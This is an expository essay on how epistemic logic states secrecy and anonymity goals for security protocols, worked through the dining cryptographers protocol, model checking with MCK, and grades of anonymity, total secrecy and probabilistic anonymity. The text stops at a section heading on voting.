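# Secrecy and anonymity as statements about knowledge: security protocol verification and its use for AI honesty claims

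## What does it mean to say that a protocol participant knows something?

A security protocol is a set of rules for exchanging messages when some listeners, or even participants, may be hostile. Most security protocols use cryptography. For example, a web browser and a bank's server run one to agree on an encryption key before they exchange any account details. The designer of a protocol usually wants certain people to find something out and everyone else not to. Wang (2010), in *Epistemic modelling and protocol dynamics*, interprets the common goals as statements about who knows what. On this reading, secrecy means that an intruder does not know certain information, anonymity means that an eavesdropper does not know who sent a message, and vote privacy means that only the voter knows how she voted. In the dining cryptographers protocol, a standard example, the goal is that no other diner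 learns which of them paid the bill.

Stated that way, the goals are too vague to check. Someone who wants to prove that no outsider learns a key must first define what counts as learning it. Pucella (2013), in *Knowledge and Security*, credits epistemic logic, the formal logic of knowledge, with several successes in supplying such definitions but fewer in turning them into practical ways of checking systems. The logic began in philosophy, where Jaakko Hintikka wrote the first book on it in 1962, and computer scientists adopted it in the 1980s to reason about machines on a network. It can also express the claim that an honest speaker asserts something only if it knows or believes it, so one might hope to use it on AI systems as well.

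For protocols, the relevant definition of knowledge comes from the "runs and systems" framework of Fagin, Halpern and colleagues in *Reasoning About Knowledge* (1995). You know a fact if it holds in every situation that fits the information you have. Hiding a fact from someone therefore means making sure there is always a situation that fits their information in which the fact is false.

### A coin under a cup

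An *agent* is any participant or observer in the system, such as a person, a program, or an attacker who only listens. Fagin and colleagues also count message buffers and wires as agents, though they grant that it sounds strange to say a wire knows facts.

Two agents, Alice and Bob, sit across a table from each other. Alice looks at a coin and puts it under a cup, heads or tails up. Bob sees only the cup. One clock tick later, Alice either lifts the cup, so that Bob sees the coin, or leaves it down. After another tick, the cup is down in either case.

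An agent's *local state* is all the information the agent has at one moment, as the model defines it. At the start, Bob's local state is "cup", and Alice's is "heads, cup down" or "tails, cup down". In a real protocol, an agent's local state might contain keys, the messages the agent has sent and received, and perhaps the reading of a clock (Halpern and O'Neill, *Anonymity and Information Hiding in Multiagent Systems*).

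A *global state* consists of every agent's local state and the state of the environment, which covers everything else that is relevant. For n agents, it is a tuple (s_e, s_1, …, s_n), where s_e is the environment's state. In this example, s_e records which side of the coin faces up and whether the cup is raised.

A *run* is one complete possible execution of the system. Formally it is a function that assigns a global state to each time 0, 1, 2 and so on. A system, in this framework, is nothing more than a nonempty set of runs. The coin system has four:

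| Run | Coin | Alice at time 1 | Bob sees at time 0 | at time 1 | at time 2 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| r1 | heads | lifts the cup | cup | heads | cup |
| r2 | heads | leaves it | cup | cup | cup |
| r3 | tails | lifts the cup | cup | tails | cup |
| r4 | tails | leaves it | cup | cup | cup |

A *point* is a run together with a time, written (r, m). The table has twelve of them.

Two points are *indistinguishable* to an agent if the agent has the same local state at both. Suppose for now that Bob's local state is only what he sees at the moment. Then he cannot distinguish (r1, 0) from (r4, 2), although the coin, the time and the history all differ.

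The formula *K_i φ*, "agent i knows φ", is true at a point if φ is true at every point that agent i cannot distinguish from it. At (r1, 1) Bob sees heads. He has that local state at no other point, and the coin lies heads up at (r1, 1), so K_B heads is true there. At (r1, 0) he sees the cup, as he also does at (r3, 0), where the coin lies tails up. K_B heads is therefore false at (r1, 0), and so is K_B tails.

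The dual of knowledge is possibility. *P_i φ*, "agent i considers φ possible", is true at a point if φ is true at at least one point that agent i cannot distinguish from it. It abbreviates ¬K_i ¬φ, which says that agent i does not know φ to be false. At (r1, 0) both P_B heads and P_B tails are true. An ignorance claim, which says that an agent does not know something, can be written with either K or P. For example, "Bob does not know that the coin is heads" means the same as "Bob considers tails possible".

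The operators also nest. At every point in the table, Bob knows that Alice knows whether the coin is heads or tails, written K_B (K_A heads ∨ K_A tails). At (r1, 0), however, he does not know that she knows it is heads. Protocol analysis requires nesting because it often matters whether one party knows that the other has received a message.

Under this definition of K_i, whatever an agent knows is true. The agent knows a fact only if it holds at every point the agent cannot distinguish from the actual one, and the actual point is always among these. Beliefs can be false, so a logic of belief needs a different relation between points.

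### Knowledge ascribed from outside

Under this definition, an analyst determines whether Bob knows something by comparing his local state across the whole table of runs, which Bob may never have seen. The definition does not refer to Bob's thoughts, and Fagin and colleagues call it an external notion of knowledge. They do not assume that agents compute what they know or could answer a question about it.

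*What Can Machines Know?* (Fagin, Halpern and Vardi, 1986) contrasts this external approach with the classical approach in AI, in which a machine counts as knowing the facts encoded in its internal data structures, such as stored logical formulas. Under the external approach, a machine knows a fact if that fact holds whenever the machine is in its present state. A smoke detector whose relay closes only when there is smoke therefore knows, once the relay has closed, that there is smoke, even though no component of the detector represents smoke in any language.

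The logic has two laws called introspection. If an agent knows φ, it knows that it knows φ, and if it does not know φ, it knows that it does not. Both laws mean only that K_i φ has the same truth value at all the points agent i cannot tell apart, because its truth depends only on i's local state. They hold for the smoke detector too, so they can hardly describe self-examination.

What an agent knows depends on what the modeler puts in its local state and which runs the modeler includes in the system. The framework does not determine either choice. Fagin and colleagues ask whether a model of a poker game should include one player's unhappy childhood, and describe finding a good representation as "far more of an art than a science".

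### How much an agent remembers

The first decision includes a choice about memory. Huang and van der Meyden (2013) define the standard options in *Symbolic Synthesis of Knowledge-based Program Implementations with Synchronous Semantics*.

Under *observational semantics*, an agent's local state at time m consists only of its observation at time m. I used this convention for Bob above.

 At (r1, 2), with the cup back down, he no longer knows how the coin lies, although he saw it a moment earlier.

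Under *perfect recall* the local state at time m is the whole sequence of observations from time 0 to time m. At (r1, 2) Bob's local state is then "cup, heads, cup", which occurs in no other run, and he still knows that the coin is heads. At (r2, 2) it is "cup, cup, cup", which also occurs in r4, and he does not know. (Huang and van der Meyden also define a clock semantics, which lies between the two: the agent has its current observation and the time.)

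Perfect recall is an idealisation. Fagin and colleagues pointed out in 1986 that an agent that never forgets needs unbounded memory in general, though for a short exchange it only needs enough to store the history. An eavesdropper who records the exchange on a hard disk comes close enough. Perfect recall is also the cautious assumption for secrecy. Two points with the same history have the same current observation, so an agent with perfect recall can distinguish everything that an agent without memory can, and often more. If Bob cannot work out which way up the coin is with perfect recall, he cannot do it under observational semantics either. However, *Optimizing Epistemic Model Checking using Conditional Independence* (van der Meyden, 2016) describes perfect recall as the most computationally demanding convention to check, because the number of variables grows quickly.

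### Which runs belong to the system

The second decision can matter just as much. Suppose Alice always lifts the cup if the coin is heads and leaves it if the coin is tails. Then only r1 and r4 remain. At (r4, 1), Bob has seen the cup twice and has never seen the coin. If he has perfect recall, he knows that the coin is tails, because r1 does not contain that sequence of observations. He has the same observations as before, and the extra knowledge comes entirely from the shorter list of runs.

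It is easy to miss that this model assumes Bob knows everything that follows from Alice's habit, whether or not anyone told him about it. Fagin and colleagues give a similar example of a knowledge base, a program that receives facts and answers queries. If the convention is that the program receives p first whenever p is true, then when it receives a different fact first, it knows that p is false.

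### Knowing everything that follows

Under this definition, an agent knows everything that follows from what it knows, a property logicians call *logical omniscience*. If φ and φ ⇒ ψ both hold at every point the agent cannot distinguish from the actual one, then ψ holds at all of those points too, so K_i φ and K_i (φ ⇒ ψ) together imply K_i ψ. An agent also knows every fact that holds throughout the system, including all logical truths.

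No real reasoner is logically omniscient. Under this definition, if Bob's local state contains a large number that is the product of two primes, Bob "knows" the primes, even if no computer could find them in his lifetime. Halpern, Moses and Vardi, in *Algorithmic Knowledge*, give the example of an expert and a novice at blackjack, who can have the same information but differ in what they can compute from it. They regard omniscience as harmless for many analyses in which a designer ascribes the knowledge. It becomes a problem when the agent has to act on what it knows, because the agent must then compute that knowledge itself.

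Treating agents as perfect reasoners is a cautious assumption for claims of ignorance. If a perfect reasoner with Bob's information could not tell which side of the coin is up, Bob can't either. The assumption can be too cautious, though, because encryption often protects a message by making it hard to compute, even when the available information determines its content. For claims that an agent does know something, the assumption is not cautious enough, since it may count the agent as knowing a fact that it could never produce.

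### Comparing runs with one another

Much of ordinary program verification deals with safety properties. A safety property holds if no execution ever reaches a state defined as bad. Pucella points out in a footnote that one can check a safety property by examining each execution on its own, whereas checking a property about knowledge requires examining each execution in the context of all the others.

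In the coin example, "Alice never lifts the cup" is a safety property. Run r2 satisfies it and r1 violates it, whatever other runs the system contains. The claim that Bob, with perfect recall, does not know at (r2, 1) that the coin is heads does depend on other runs. It is true only because the system contains r4, where he also sees the cup twice but the coin is tails. If r4 were removed, the claim would become false even though r2 had not changed, so the claim cannot be checked by inspecting r2 alone.

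Removing runs from a system never breaks a safety property, so any safety property still holds after a programmer replaces a free choice in the design with a fixed rule. But the same change can destroy secrecy, as Alice's habit with the cup did, because the removed runs may be the ones that left an observer uncertain.

Checking such claims by hand means comparing every run with every other, which soon becomes impractical. An epistemic model checker is a program that takes a finite model of a system, a convention for the local states and a formula about knowledge, and determines whether the formula holds in every run the model allows. If the formula fails, the program can often produce a counterexample.

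## How do the dining cryptographers hide who paid?

The dining cryptographers protocol is small enough to check by hand. *The Dining Cryptographers Problem* (Chaum, 1988) introduced it with a story. Three cryptographers are having dinner when the waiter tells them that someone has arranged to pay the bill anonymously. The payer may be one of the three or the US National Security Agency (NSA). The cryptographers respect each other's right to pay in secret, but they want to know whether the NSA is paying.

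Chaum wanted to let people send messages over a network without anyone finding out who sent what, even if an eavesdropper can trace every transmission to the machine it came from. Similarly, everyone at the dinner table can hear who is speaking. The anonymous message there is a single bit, "I paid". To send a longer message, the cryptographers repeat the protocol, one bit per round.

### The protocol

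Three cryptographers are numbered 1, 2 and 3. Each pair tosses a fair coin behind a menu so that the other cryptographer cannot see it. The results are c12, c13 and c23, with 0 for heads and 1 for tails. Cryptographer 1 sees c12 and c13 but not c23.

Each cryptographer then compares the two coins she can see. If she did not pay, she announces 0 when they match and 1 when they differ. If she paid, she announces the opposite.

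This comparison is the operation "exclusive or", or XOR, written ⊕: x ⊕ y is 0 if x and y are equal and 1 if they differ. XOR with 1 flips a bit, and XOR with 0 leaves it alone. Let p1 be 1 if cryptographer 1 paid and 0 if she did not, and likewise for p2 and p3. The announcements are then

```
a1 = p1 ⊕ c12 ⊕ c13
a2 = p2 ⊕ c12 ⊕ c23
a3 = p3 ⊕ c13 ⊕ c23
```

Anyone who hears all three can XOR them together. The order of the terms makes no difference, every coin appears exactly twice, and a bit XORed with itself is 0. The coins therefore cancel:

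```
a1 ⊕ a2 ⊕ a3 = p1 ⊕ p2 ⊕ p3
```

At most one of the three paid, so the result is 1 if one of them did and 0 if none did. The protocol uses no encryption and, as Pucella points out, achieves a form of confidentiality without complex operations.

An ordinary model checker can confirm that the XOR is correct without reasoning about knowledge, because it can check each run separately. PRISM, a model checker for systems that make random choices, has confirmed it for up to 20 cryptographers. Whether the announcements also reveal *which* cryptographer paid is a question about knowledge, so checking it requires comparing runs.

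### What cryptographer 1 can work out

Suppose cryptographer 1 did not pay, and sees c12 = 0 and c13 = 1. Before the others speak, there are six runs that she cannot rule out:

| Who paid | c23 | 2 announces | 3 announces |
|---|---|---|---|
| NSA | 0 | 0 | 1 |
| NSA | 1 | 1 | 0 |
| 2 | 0 | 1 | 1 |
| 2 | 1 | 0 | 0 |
| 3 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| 3 | 1 | 1 | 1 |

Her own announcement is 1 in all six, since her coins differ and she did not pay.

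Suppose she hears 0 from both cryptographer 2 and cryptographer 3. The XOR of the three announcements is 1 ⊕ 0 ⊕ 0 = 1, so someone at the table paid, and she knows it wasn't her. Cryptographer 2 announced p2 ⊕ 0 ⊕ c23 = 0, so p2 equals c23. Cryptographer 3 announced p3 ⊕ 1 ⊕ c23 = 0, so p3 is the opposite of c23. If c23 = 0, then 3 paid, and if c23 = 1, then 2 paid. She can't see c23, the coin the other two tossed without her, so she knows that one of them paid but not which one.

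Now suppose she hears 0 from cryptographer 2 but 1 from cryptographer 3. The XOR is 1 ⊕ 0 ⊕ 1 = 0. As before, p2 equals c23, but now p3 does too, so either neither of them paid (c23 = 0) or both did (c23 = 1). She cannot tell which from the announcements alone, because two payers flip two announcements and the flips cancel. But at most one party pays, so they cannot both have paid, and the table therefore has only one row with these announcements. She knows that nobody at the table paid. Chaum states the same condition when he claims that an even number of "different"s means the NSA is paying, and he notes that any even number of senders produces a total of 0.

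When cryptographer 1 removes the coins she knows, she gets p2 ⊕ c23 from 2's announcement and p3 ⊕ c23 from 3's. The coin she cannot see, c23, hides both bits. If she XORs the two results, the coin cancels and she gets p2 ⊕ p3, from which she learns whether one of them paid. She cannot remove the coin from either bit separately. Chaum compares this to a one-time pad, a cipher that combines a message with a random key used only once.

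He also proves a general version, for any number of participants and any arrangement of shared coins. If chains of coins that the observer cannot see link a group of participants together, the observer learns only whether an odd or even number of people in the group flipped their announcements. The proof also covers probabilities. In the example, whichever of 2 and 3 paid, cryptographer 1 hears "0, 0" half the time and "1, 1" half the time. So if she thought beforehand that 2 was three times as likely as 3 to pay, she has no reason to change her mind afterwards.

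### Thirty-two runs

In the model, the payer is cryptographer 1, 2, 3 or the NSA, and the three coins can land in eight ways. The payer and the coins determine the announcements, so there are 4 × 8 = 32 runs. At the end of each run, cryptographer 1's local state consists of whether she paid, how her two coins landed and the three announcements.

The table above covers the six runs in which she did not pay and saw c12 = 0 and c13 = 1. After the announcements, she can identify two of these runs exactly, and the other four form two pairs whose members she cannot tell apart. The same pattern holds for the three other ways her coins can fall, so the runs in which she did not pay consist of 8 that she can identify and 8 pairs. In the remaining 8 runs, she paid. She then knows that p2 is 0, so she can work out c23 from 2's announcement and identify the run.

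| Who paid | Number of runs | Grouping for cryptographer 1 |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 8 | 8 single runs |
| NSA | 8 | 8 single runs |
| 2 or 3 | 16 | 8 pairs, with one run for each payer |

Each run in which cryptographer 2 paid can be paired with a run that differs only in that cryptographer 3 paid and the coin c23 landed the other way. Cryptographer 2's announcement is the same in both runs, because the change in whether she paid reverses it and the change in the coin reverses it again. The same holds for cryptographer 3's announcement. Cryptographer 1 therefore sees and hears exactly the same things in both runs.

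A stranger at the next table who hears the announcements but sees no coins knows less than the cryptographers do. A cryptographer paid in 24 of the runs, and these runs produce only four different sets of announcements, with six runs producing each set. Each cryptographer paid in two of those six runs, so the stranger learns that a cryptographer paid but cannot rule out any of the three.

Two cryptographers who compare notes can work out whether the third paid. If neither of them paid and the XOR is 1, the third did. Chaum accepts this because no protocol can hide a sender when everyone else cooperates against her.

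### The anonymity claim as a formula

In words, the claim about cryptographer 1 goes like this. If she did not pay, then after the announcements either she knows that nobody at the table paid, or she knows that one of the other two did and does not know which. van der Meyden writes this as a formula. With his cryptographers renumbered from 1, it is

```
¬paid1 ⇒ (  K_1 (¬paid2 ∧ ¬paid3)
          ∨ ( K_1 (paid2 ∨ paid3) ∧ ¬K_1 paid2 ∧ ¬K_1 paid3 ) )
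```

where paid1 is true when p1 = 1. The count of runs is enough to check it.

- In the 8 runs where cryptographer 1 paid, ¬paid1 is false, so the whole formula is true automatically.
- In the 8 runs where the NSA paid, she cannot confuse the actual run with any other, so she knows everything that is true in it, including that 2 and 3 did not pay.
- In the other 16 runs she cannot distinguish two runs. "2 or 3 paid" is true in both, so she knows it. "2 paid" is false in one of them and "3 paid" is false in the other, so she knows neither.

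The formula is therefore true at the end of all 32 runs, but not earlier. Before the others speak, a cryptographer 1 who did not pay does not yet know whether the NSA or a colleague did, so both of the formula's alternatives are false. The specification therefore has to include a time. The model checker MCK, which van der Meyden uses, evaluates formulas at the start of every run, and the operator X moves the evaluation one clock tick forward. His protocol takes three ticks, so he puts three X's in front of the formula.

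The formula requires the protocol to reveal whether the NSA paid, as well as to hide which cryptographer paid if one of them did. If all three cryptographers kept quiet, the payer's identity would stay secret, but nobody would find out whether the NSA paid. Cryptographer 1 would not know that "2 or 3 paid", so the formula would be false.

This half of the specification is easy to leave out. The last alternative in the script in van der Meyden's appendix requires only that the cryptographer consider each of her colleagues a possible payer (P_1 paid2 ∧ P_1 paid3 in the present numbering). A protocol in which nobody announces anything would pass that test. With more than three cryptographers, though, the version with P is stricter about anonymity, because it requires every colleague to remain a suspect, while the version with ¬K is still true if the observer has narrowed the list to two. Researchers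 have defined several grades of anonymity along these lines.

The formula is only about cryptographer 1, but the protocol treats all three alike, so the corresponding formulas hold for 2 and 3. Since ¬K_1 paid2 is true throughout the system, cryptographer 2 knows before she pays that cryptographer 1 will not find out from the protocol.

The formula omits Chaum's point about the odds. Van der Meyden treats a coin toss as a free choice between 0 and 1, with no probabilities attached, so the formula guarantees only that cryptographer 1 cannot rule out either colleague as the payer. It would still hold if she thought one more likely than the other.

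### Telling the program who sees what

Nobody types 32 runs into a model checker. The user writes a short program for each agent, and the checker generates the runs from it. The user must also list the variables that each agent can observe. Here is a simplified version of van der Meyden's program:

```
At the start: at most one of paid1, paid2, paid3 is 1

Cryptographer 1
  observes: paid1, c12, c13, say1, say2, say3
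  tick 1:   c12 := random bit
  tick 2:   say1 := paid1 ⊕ c12 ⊕ c13

Cryptographer 2
  observes: paid2, c12, c23, say1, say2, say3
  tick 1:   c23 := random bit
  tick 2:   say2 := paid2 ⊕ c12 ⊕ c23

Cryptographer 3
  observes: paid3, c13, c23, say1, say2, say3
  tick 1:   c13 := random bit
  tick 2:   say3 := paid3 ⊕ c13 ⊕ c23
```

His own version needs a third tick because each cryptographer copies her coin into a separate variable for her neighbour. She writes to that variable but does not observe it, which costs her nothing, since she already knows what she put there. (MCK would generate more than 32 runs, because any variable that the starting condition leaves open may begin as 0 or 1. The program overwrites those values before anyone uses them.)

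The starting condition requires that at most one cryptographer paid. The body of van der Meyden's paper misprints an "and" in this condition as "or", which would allow any two of the three to pay. The formula would then be false, because if cryptographer 1 heard 0 from 2 and 1 from 3, she could no longer tell whether both of them had paid or neither had. The script in his appendix has the correct condition.

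The "observes" lines determine the local states. Al-Bataineh and van der Meyden (2010), in *Epistemic Model Checking for Knowledge-Based Program Implementation*, explain that an agent's observation at any moment is the current values of the variables on her list. Under perfect recall, MCK keeps the whole sequence of observations. The user never has to write down what cryptographer 1 can deduce from her coins and the announcements, because MCK works this out by comparing runs.

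In MCK's input language, the user marks such a variable with the word "observable". Gammie and van der Meyden's *MCK*, which introduced the tool, gives the example of a robot that moves along a line of eight positions. The robot's position is an ordinary variable, while its sensor reading, which may be off by one, is observable. So the robot can know where it is only as far as its sensor readings allow.

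Van der Meyden writes the protocol once, and all three agents run it. The "paid" bits form a list with one entry per cryptographer, and the line that creates each agent connects only her own entry to the variable marked observable. The announcements form another list, which every agent observes in full.

Other models include less information in each cryptographer's local state. In the version described in *Symbolic Model Checking for Temporal-Epistemic Logics* (Lomuscio and Penczek, 2007), the local state records only whether her two coins match, whether she paid, and whether the number of "different"s is odd or even. At the end of the protocol, cryptographer 1 then has only 6 possible local states, compared with 24 in the model above. Under their formula, which is similar to van der Meyden's, if the number is odd and she did not pay, she comes to know that one of the others did, but not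 which one. The formula holds in their model too, but their local state leaves out who announced what. If the cryptographers instead announced whether they had paid, without using coins, the number would be odd in exactly the same cases and the formula would still be true, even though everyone would hear who paid.

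## What kinds of anonymity and secrecy can be stated as lack of knowledge?

"Anonymous" has several meanings, and the dining cryptographers formula expresses only one. Halpern and O'Neill compare anonymity claims by what information the system must hide, from whom, and how well.

A claim that something is hidden from an observer must specify what that observer can see, because two observers of the same event may see different parts of it. Halpern and O'Neill borrow an example from Schneider and Sidiropoulos, who had studied anonymity in another formalism. One of two people will donate to a charity. If it is Ann, she gives $5, and if it is Ben, he gives $10. An observer who sees the amount knows who the donor is, while one who sees only that a donation arrived does not. The same definition of anonymity gives different results for the two observers because their local states differ.

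### Grades of anonymity

An agent's anonymity can be stronger or weaker. The formula θ(i, a) means that agent i has performed action a or will perform it later in the run. It includes future actions because an observer who learns in advance that i will act has already identified i, even if he never learns when the action happens. In the table, j is the observer, and each formula must be true at every point of the system.

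| Grade | Formula | Plain reading |
|---|---|---|
| Minimal anonymity | ¬K_j θ(i, a) | j is never certain that i did it |
| Total anonymity | θ(i, a) ⇒ P_j θ(i′, a) for every agent i′ except j | if i did it, then for all j knows anyone but j could have |
| Anonymity up to a set S | θ(i, a) ⇒ P_j θ(i′, a) for every i′ in S | if i did it, then for all j knows any member of S could have |
| k-anonymity | θ(i, a) ⇒ for some set of k agents, P_j θ(i′, a) for every i′ in the set | if i did it, j has at least k suspects |

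Minimal anonymity is a weak guarantee and total anonymity is usually unattainable, so most claims concern a particular *anonymity set*. This is the set of agents who could have performed the action, as far as the observer knows.

In the dining cryptographers protocol, a payment by cryptographer 2 is anonymous up to {2, 3} with respect to cryptographer 1, and up to {1, 2, 3} with respect to the stranger at the next table. It is also totally anonymous with respect to cryptographer 1 if the three cryptographers are the only agents in the model, but not if the NSA is an agent too, because the announcements let cryptographer 1 rule out the NSA.

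Under k-anonymity, the set of suspects may change from run to run. Halpern and O'Neill give the example of Herbivore, a message system that sorts its users into groups, each of which runs the dining cryptographers protocol. A sender is anonymous within her group, so the system provides k-anonymity if every group has at least k members. The sender herself always counts as one of the k suspects, because the observer j can never rule out something true. k-anonymity therefore guarantees only k − 1 other suspects, which means 1-anonymity guarantees nothing.

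### When everyone is a suspect and the culprit is known anyway

One would expect total anonymity to imply minimal anonymity. It does, but only under two conditions that Halpern and O'Neill spell out.

Total anonymity is a meaningful condition only when there are at least three agents. If i and j are the only two, it requires only that j consider it possible that i did it, which is automatically true when i did. In their example, a student with a single roommate can't leave her dirty dishes anonymously.

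The action must also be one that at most one agent performs in any run. Suppose three students all left dirty dishes and the fourth saw the three piles. The formula for total anonymity is true because she considers it possible that each of them did it, even though she knows that each of them did.

Suppose both conditions hold and i did it. There is a third agent i′ besides i and the observer j. By total anonymity, j cannot distinguish the actual point from one where i′ did it. Only one agent can have done it, so i did not do it at that other point. Hence j does not know that i did it.

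### Knowing something about the sender without knowing the name

An observer may be unable to name the author of any of ten anonymous letters and still know that one person wrote them all. Hughes and Shmatikov, in *Information Hiding, Anonymity and Privacy*, describe this kind of partial knowledge with what they call function views. They treat "who sent what" as a function from messages to senders and record three things that an observer may know about it:

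- its *graph*: for each message, which senders are still candidates
- its *image*: which people certainly sent something, even if the observer cannot say what
- its *kernel*: which messages certainly came from the same sender, even if the observer cannot say who

If, as far as the observer knows, each message could always have come from any of at least k senders, the system provides essentially k-anonymity. If the observer can never tell that two messages share a sender, the messages are unlinkable.

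Hughes and Shmatikov wanted function views to be a layer between logics of knowledge, which make it easy to state what a system should hide, and process algebras, which make it easy to describe the system. Halpern and O'Neill reply that runs already serve both purposes. They prove that anonymity up to a set matches one of the function-view properties, provided that property is applied only where a member of the set performed the action. They can also use P to state unlinkability, by saying that the observer considers it possible that two different agents performed the two actions. Function views are therefore a convenient way to state claims the logic could already express.

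### Total secrecy

Anonymity hides the single fact that an agent did a certain thing. Halpern and O'Neill's *Secrecy in Multiagent Systems* defines a much broader property. Agent i maintains *total secrecy* with respect to j if ¬K_j φ is true at every point, for every non-trivial fact φ that depends only on i's local state. Non-trivial means that φ is false at some point of the system, and depending only on i's local state means that i always knows whether φ is true. Equivalently, every local state that i ever has must occur together with every local state that j ever has, so j can never rule out any of i's possible local states.

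Total secrecy does not imply total anonymity. Suppose Dave looks away from a collection box while Carol either puts a banknote in it or doesn't. Erin stands in front of Dave the whole time and gives nothing. Dave learns nothing that depends on Carol's state, so Carol has total secrecy with respect to him. But he knows that Erin did not give, which Carol's secrecy does not cover because it is a fact about Erin. So if Carol gave, her gift is not totally anonymous.

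Total anonymity does not imply total secrecy either. If the cryptographers are the only agents, a payment by cryptographer 2 is totally anonymous with respect to cryptographer 1. But total secrecy fails because cryptographer 1 sees the coin c12, which is part of cryptographer 2's local state. Cryptographer 1 also learns that cryptographer 2 did not pay when the NSA pays, as the protocol intends.

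Halpern and O'Neill consider total secrecy too strong for almost any imaginable system. If both agents can see a clock, j can rule out any state that i is in only at other times, so total secrecy fails for a trivial reason. They therefore offer weaker versions, including one that compares whole runs instead of points and one that protects only a chosen part of i's state.

Total secrecy is closely related to *noninterference*, which Goguen and Meseguer introduced in 1982 for computers shared by classified and unclassified users. It requires that nothing the classified users do affects what the unclassified users see. *Epistemic Temporal Logic for Information Flow Security* (Balliu, Dam and Le Guernic, 2011) adapts it to programs that start with some public and some secret values and then print output. A program satisfies this version if any two executions that start with the same public values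 print the same output, whatever the secret values are. An observer of the output then considers every initial secret value possible.

Suppose the secret is a digit from 0 to 9 and the program prints whether it is even. The observer never knows the digit, so ¬K_j (digit = d) is true throughout for every digit d. But once he sees "even" he no longer considers 3 possible, so the program violates noninterference. Minimal and total anonymity differ for the same reason, since an observer can rule out many alternatives without knowing the answer.

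### Possible but very unlikely

All these definitions treat possibility as a matter of yes or no, which Halpern and O'Neill regard as a serious problem. In their example there are 102 agents, and the observer calculates a probability of 0.99 that agent i performed the action and 0.0001 for each of the 100 other suspects. The action still counts as totally anonymous because every suspect remains possible, but agent i might not consider that enough protection.

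A bad coin has the same effect on the dining cryptographers. Suppose the coin that cryptographers 2 and 3 toss, c23, lands 0 nine times out of ten, and cryptographer 1 knows this. She considers 2 and 3 equally likely to pay, with probability q each. As in the run worked through earlier, she did not pay, she sees c12 = 0 and c13 = 1, and she hears 0 from both of the others. Two possibilities remain:

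| Who paid | c23 | Probability of the payer and the coin together |
|---|---|---|
| 3 | 0 | q × 0.9 |
| 2 | 1 | q × 0.1 |

The probability that cryptographer 3 paid is therefore 0.9q / (0.9q + 0.1q) = 0.9. If both had announced 1 instead, the same calculation would give a 90% probability that cryptographer 2 paid. So whenever one of her colleagues pays, cryptographer 1 can guess which one and be right nine times out of ten, compared with half the time if the coin were fair.

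The anonymity formula still holds at the end of all 32 runs, because the bias removes none of them. A model checker given this formula would therefore pass the protocol. It would report a fault only if c23 could never land 1, because the run in which 2 paid would then disappear.

Hughes and Shmatikov deliberately exclude this case, saying that their framework does not cover an observer who assigns 90% probability to one answer and 10% to another. They justify this by assuming that the cryptography hides how the underlying data are distributed. That holds for a fair coin but not for a biased one, so their assumption rules out the fault that an analyst would want to find.

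Halpern and O'Neill instead add probabilities to the runs. At any point, the observer's probability for a fact is its probability among the runs that fit his local state, which is how the 0.9 came about. They call an action *α-anonymous* if this is true at every point:

```
θ(i, a) ⇒ Pr_j [θ(i, a)] < α
```

In words, if i did it, then j's probability that i did it is below α. Without the condition "if i did it", the formula would also protect innocent people from suspicion, since j can consider it very likely that i did it even when i did not. Adding the condition to minimal anonymity would change nothing, because j cannot know that i did it unless i did.

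Halpern and O'Neill identify 0.5-anonymity with "probable innocence", a guarantee from Crowds, which Reiter and Rubin built in 1998 to hide who is requesting a web page. Crowds routes requests randomly, and a sender has probable innocence if she appears no more likely to be the originator than not. The match isn't quite exact, because probable innocence allows a probability of exactly 0.5, while 0.5-anonymity requires one below 0.5. In the dining cryptographers example, a fair coin and equally likely payers give exactly 0.5. With the biased coin, the payment is α-anonymous with respect to cryptographer 1 only if α is above 0.9.

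A low probability is not always enough for anonymity. Suppose Alice assigns probability 0.1 to Bob having done it and divides the rest evenly among 1,000 other people, giving each about 0.0009. Bob has 0.11-anonymity, but he is more than a hundred times as likely as anyone else to have done it, so he is still the main suspect. One remedy is to require that the observer assign the same probability to every member of the anonymity set.

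Requiring that all suspects seem equally likely can also be unreasonable. If someone gives Cornell University $5 million, some people were always likelier donors than others, and no protocol can change that. The donor can ask at most that observers learn nothing more about who gave. Halpern and O'Neill call this *conditional anonymity*. Once an observer j knows that someone other than himself performed the action, the probability he assigns to i having done it must equal the probability he would have assigned at the start if he had been told only that someone else would do it.

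This definition distinguishes two cases that are almost the same under α-anonymity. Suppose the coins are fair but cryptographer 2 is known to be generous, so that if one of the three paid, the probability is 0.8 that she did and 0.1 for each of the others. If cryptographer 1 did not pay and learns that a colleague did, she assigns cryptographer 2 a probability of 0.8 / (0.8 + 0.1), or about 0.89. That is close to the 0.9 from the biased coin, but conditional anonymity holds because she learned nothing from the protocol about which colleague paid. With the biased coin it fails, because the announcements raised her probability for one colleague from 0.5 to 0.9. According to Halpern and O'Neill, Chaum's original proof establishes conditional anonymity.

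Conditional anonymity can't replace the other definitions either. If everyone is certain from the start that cryptographer 2 will pay, she has conditional anonymity because the protocol reveals nothing new about her, even though everyone knows she paid.

### Hiding what someone did

Anonymity starts from an action and hides the agent. Tsukada, Mano and colleagues (2010), in *Anonymity, Privacy, Onymity, and Identity*, use "privacy" for the reverse, which starts from an agent and hides the action. Agent i's performing a is private up to a set T of actions if

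```
θ(i, a) ⇒ P_j θ(i, a′)   for every action a′ in T
```

If agent i performed action a, then for all observer j knows, i could have performed any action in the set T. In an election, anonymity means that the observer can't tell who cast a given vote, and privacy means that the observer can't tell how a given person voted.

In a unanimous election, anonymity can hold even though nobody has any privacy. If all the votes go to one candidate, an observer who sees the tally knows that everyone voted for her. He therefore considers it possible that any given voter did, so the formula for anonymity up to the set of voters is true. This is the dirty dishes problem again, since many people perform the same action. Tsukada and colleagues point out that "at most one agent performs each action" is an unnatural assumption for voting, whereas "each agent performs at most one action" fits it well. Under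 the second assumption, privacy up to a set of two or more candidates ensures that the observer never knows how someone voted.

They also use a stronger property, *role interchangeability*, which can provide both anonymity and privacy. If one voter chose candidate x and another chose y, the observer must consider it possible that they voted the other way round. Mano and colleagues proved in an earlier paper that FOO, an electronic voting protocol, has this property. It follows that each vote is anonymous up to the set of eligible voters, and private up to the set of candidates who received votes.

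Two steps that each hide something may fail to hide it when combined. Tsukada, Sakurada and colleagues (2013), in *An Epistemic Approach to Compositional Reasoning about Anonymity and Privacy*, give the example of a members-only bulletin board. Members register pseudonyms, and articles are posted under those pseudonyms. An observer may be unable to tell which member has which pseudonym, or which pseudonym posted which article. But if he knows that a certain member would never submit a certain improper article, he can rule her out, which leaves one fewer possible author. Tsukada and colleagues show that the combined system preserves anonymity if the two steps are independent in a sense they define.

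### When the voter helps the observer

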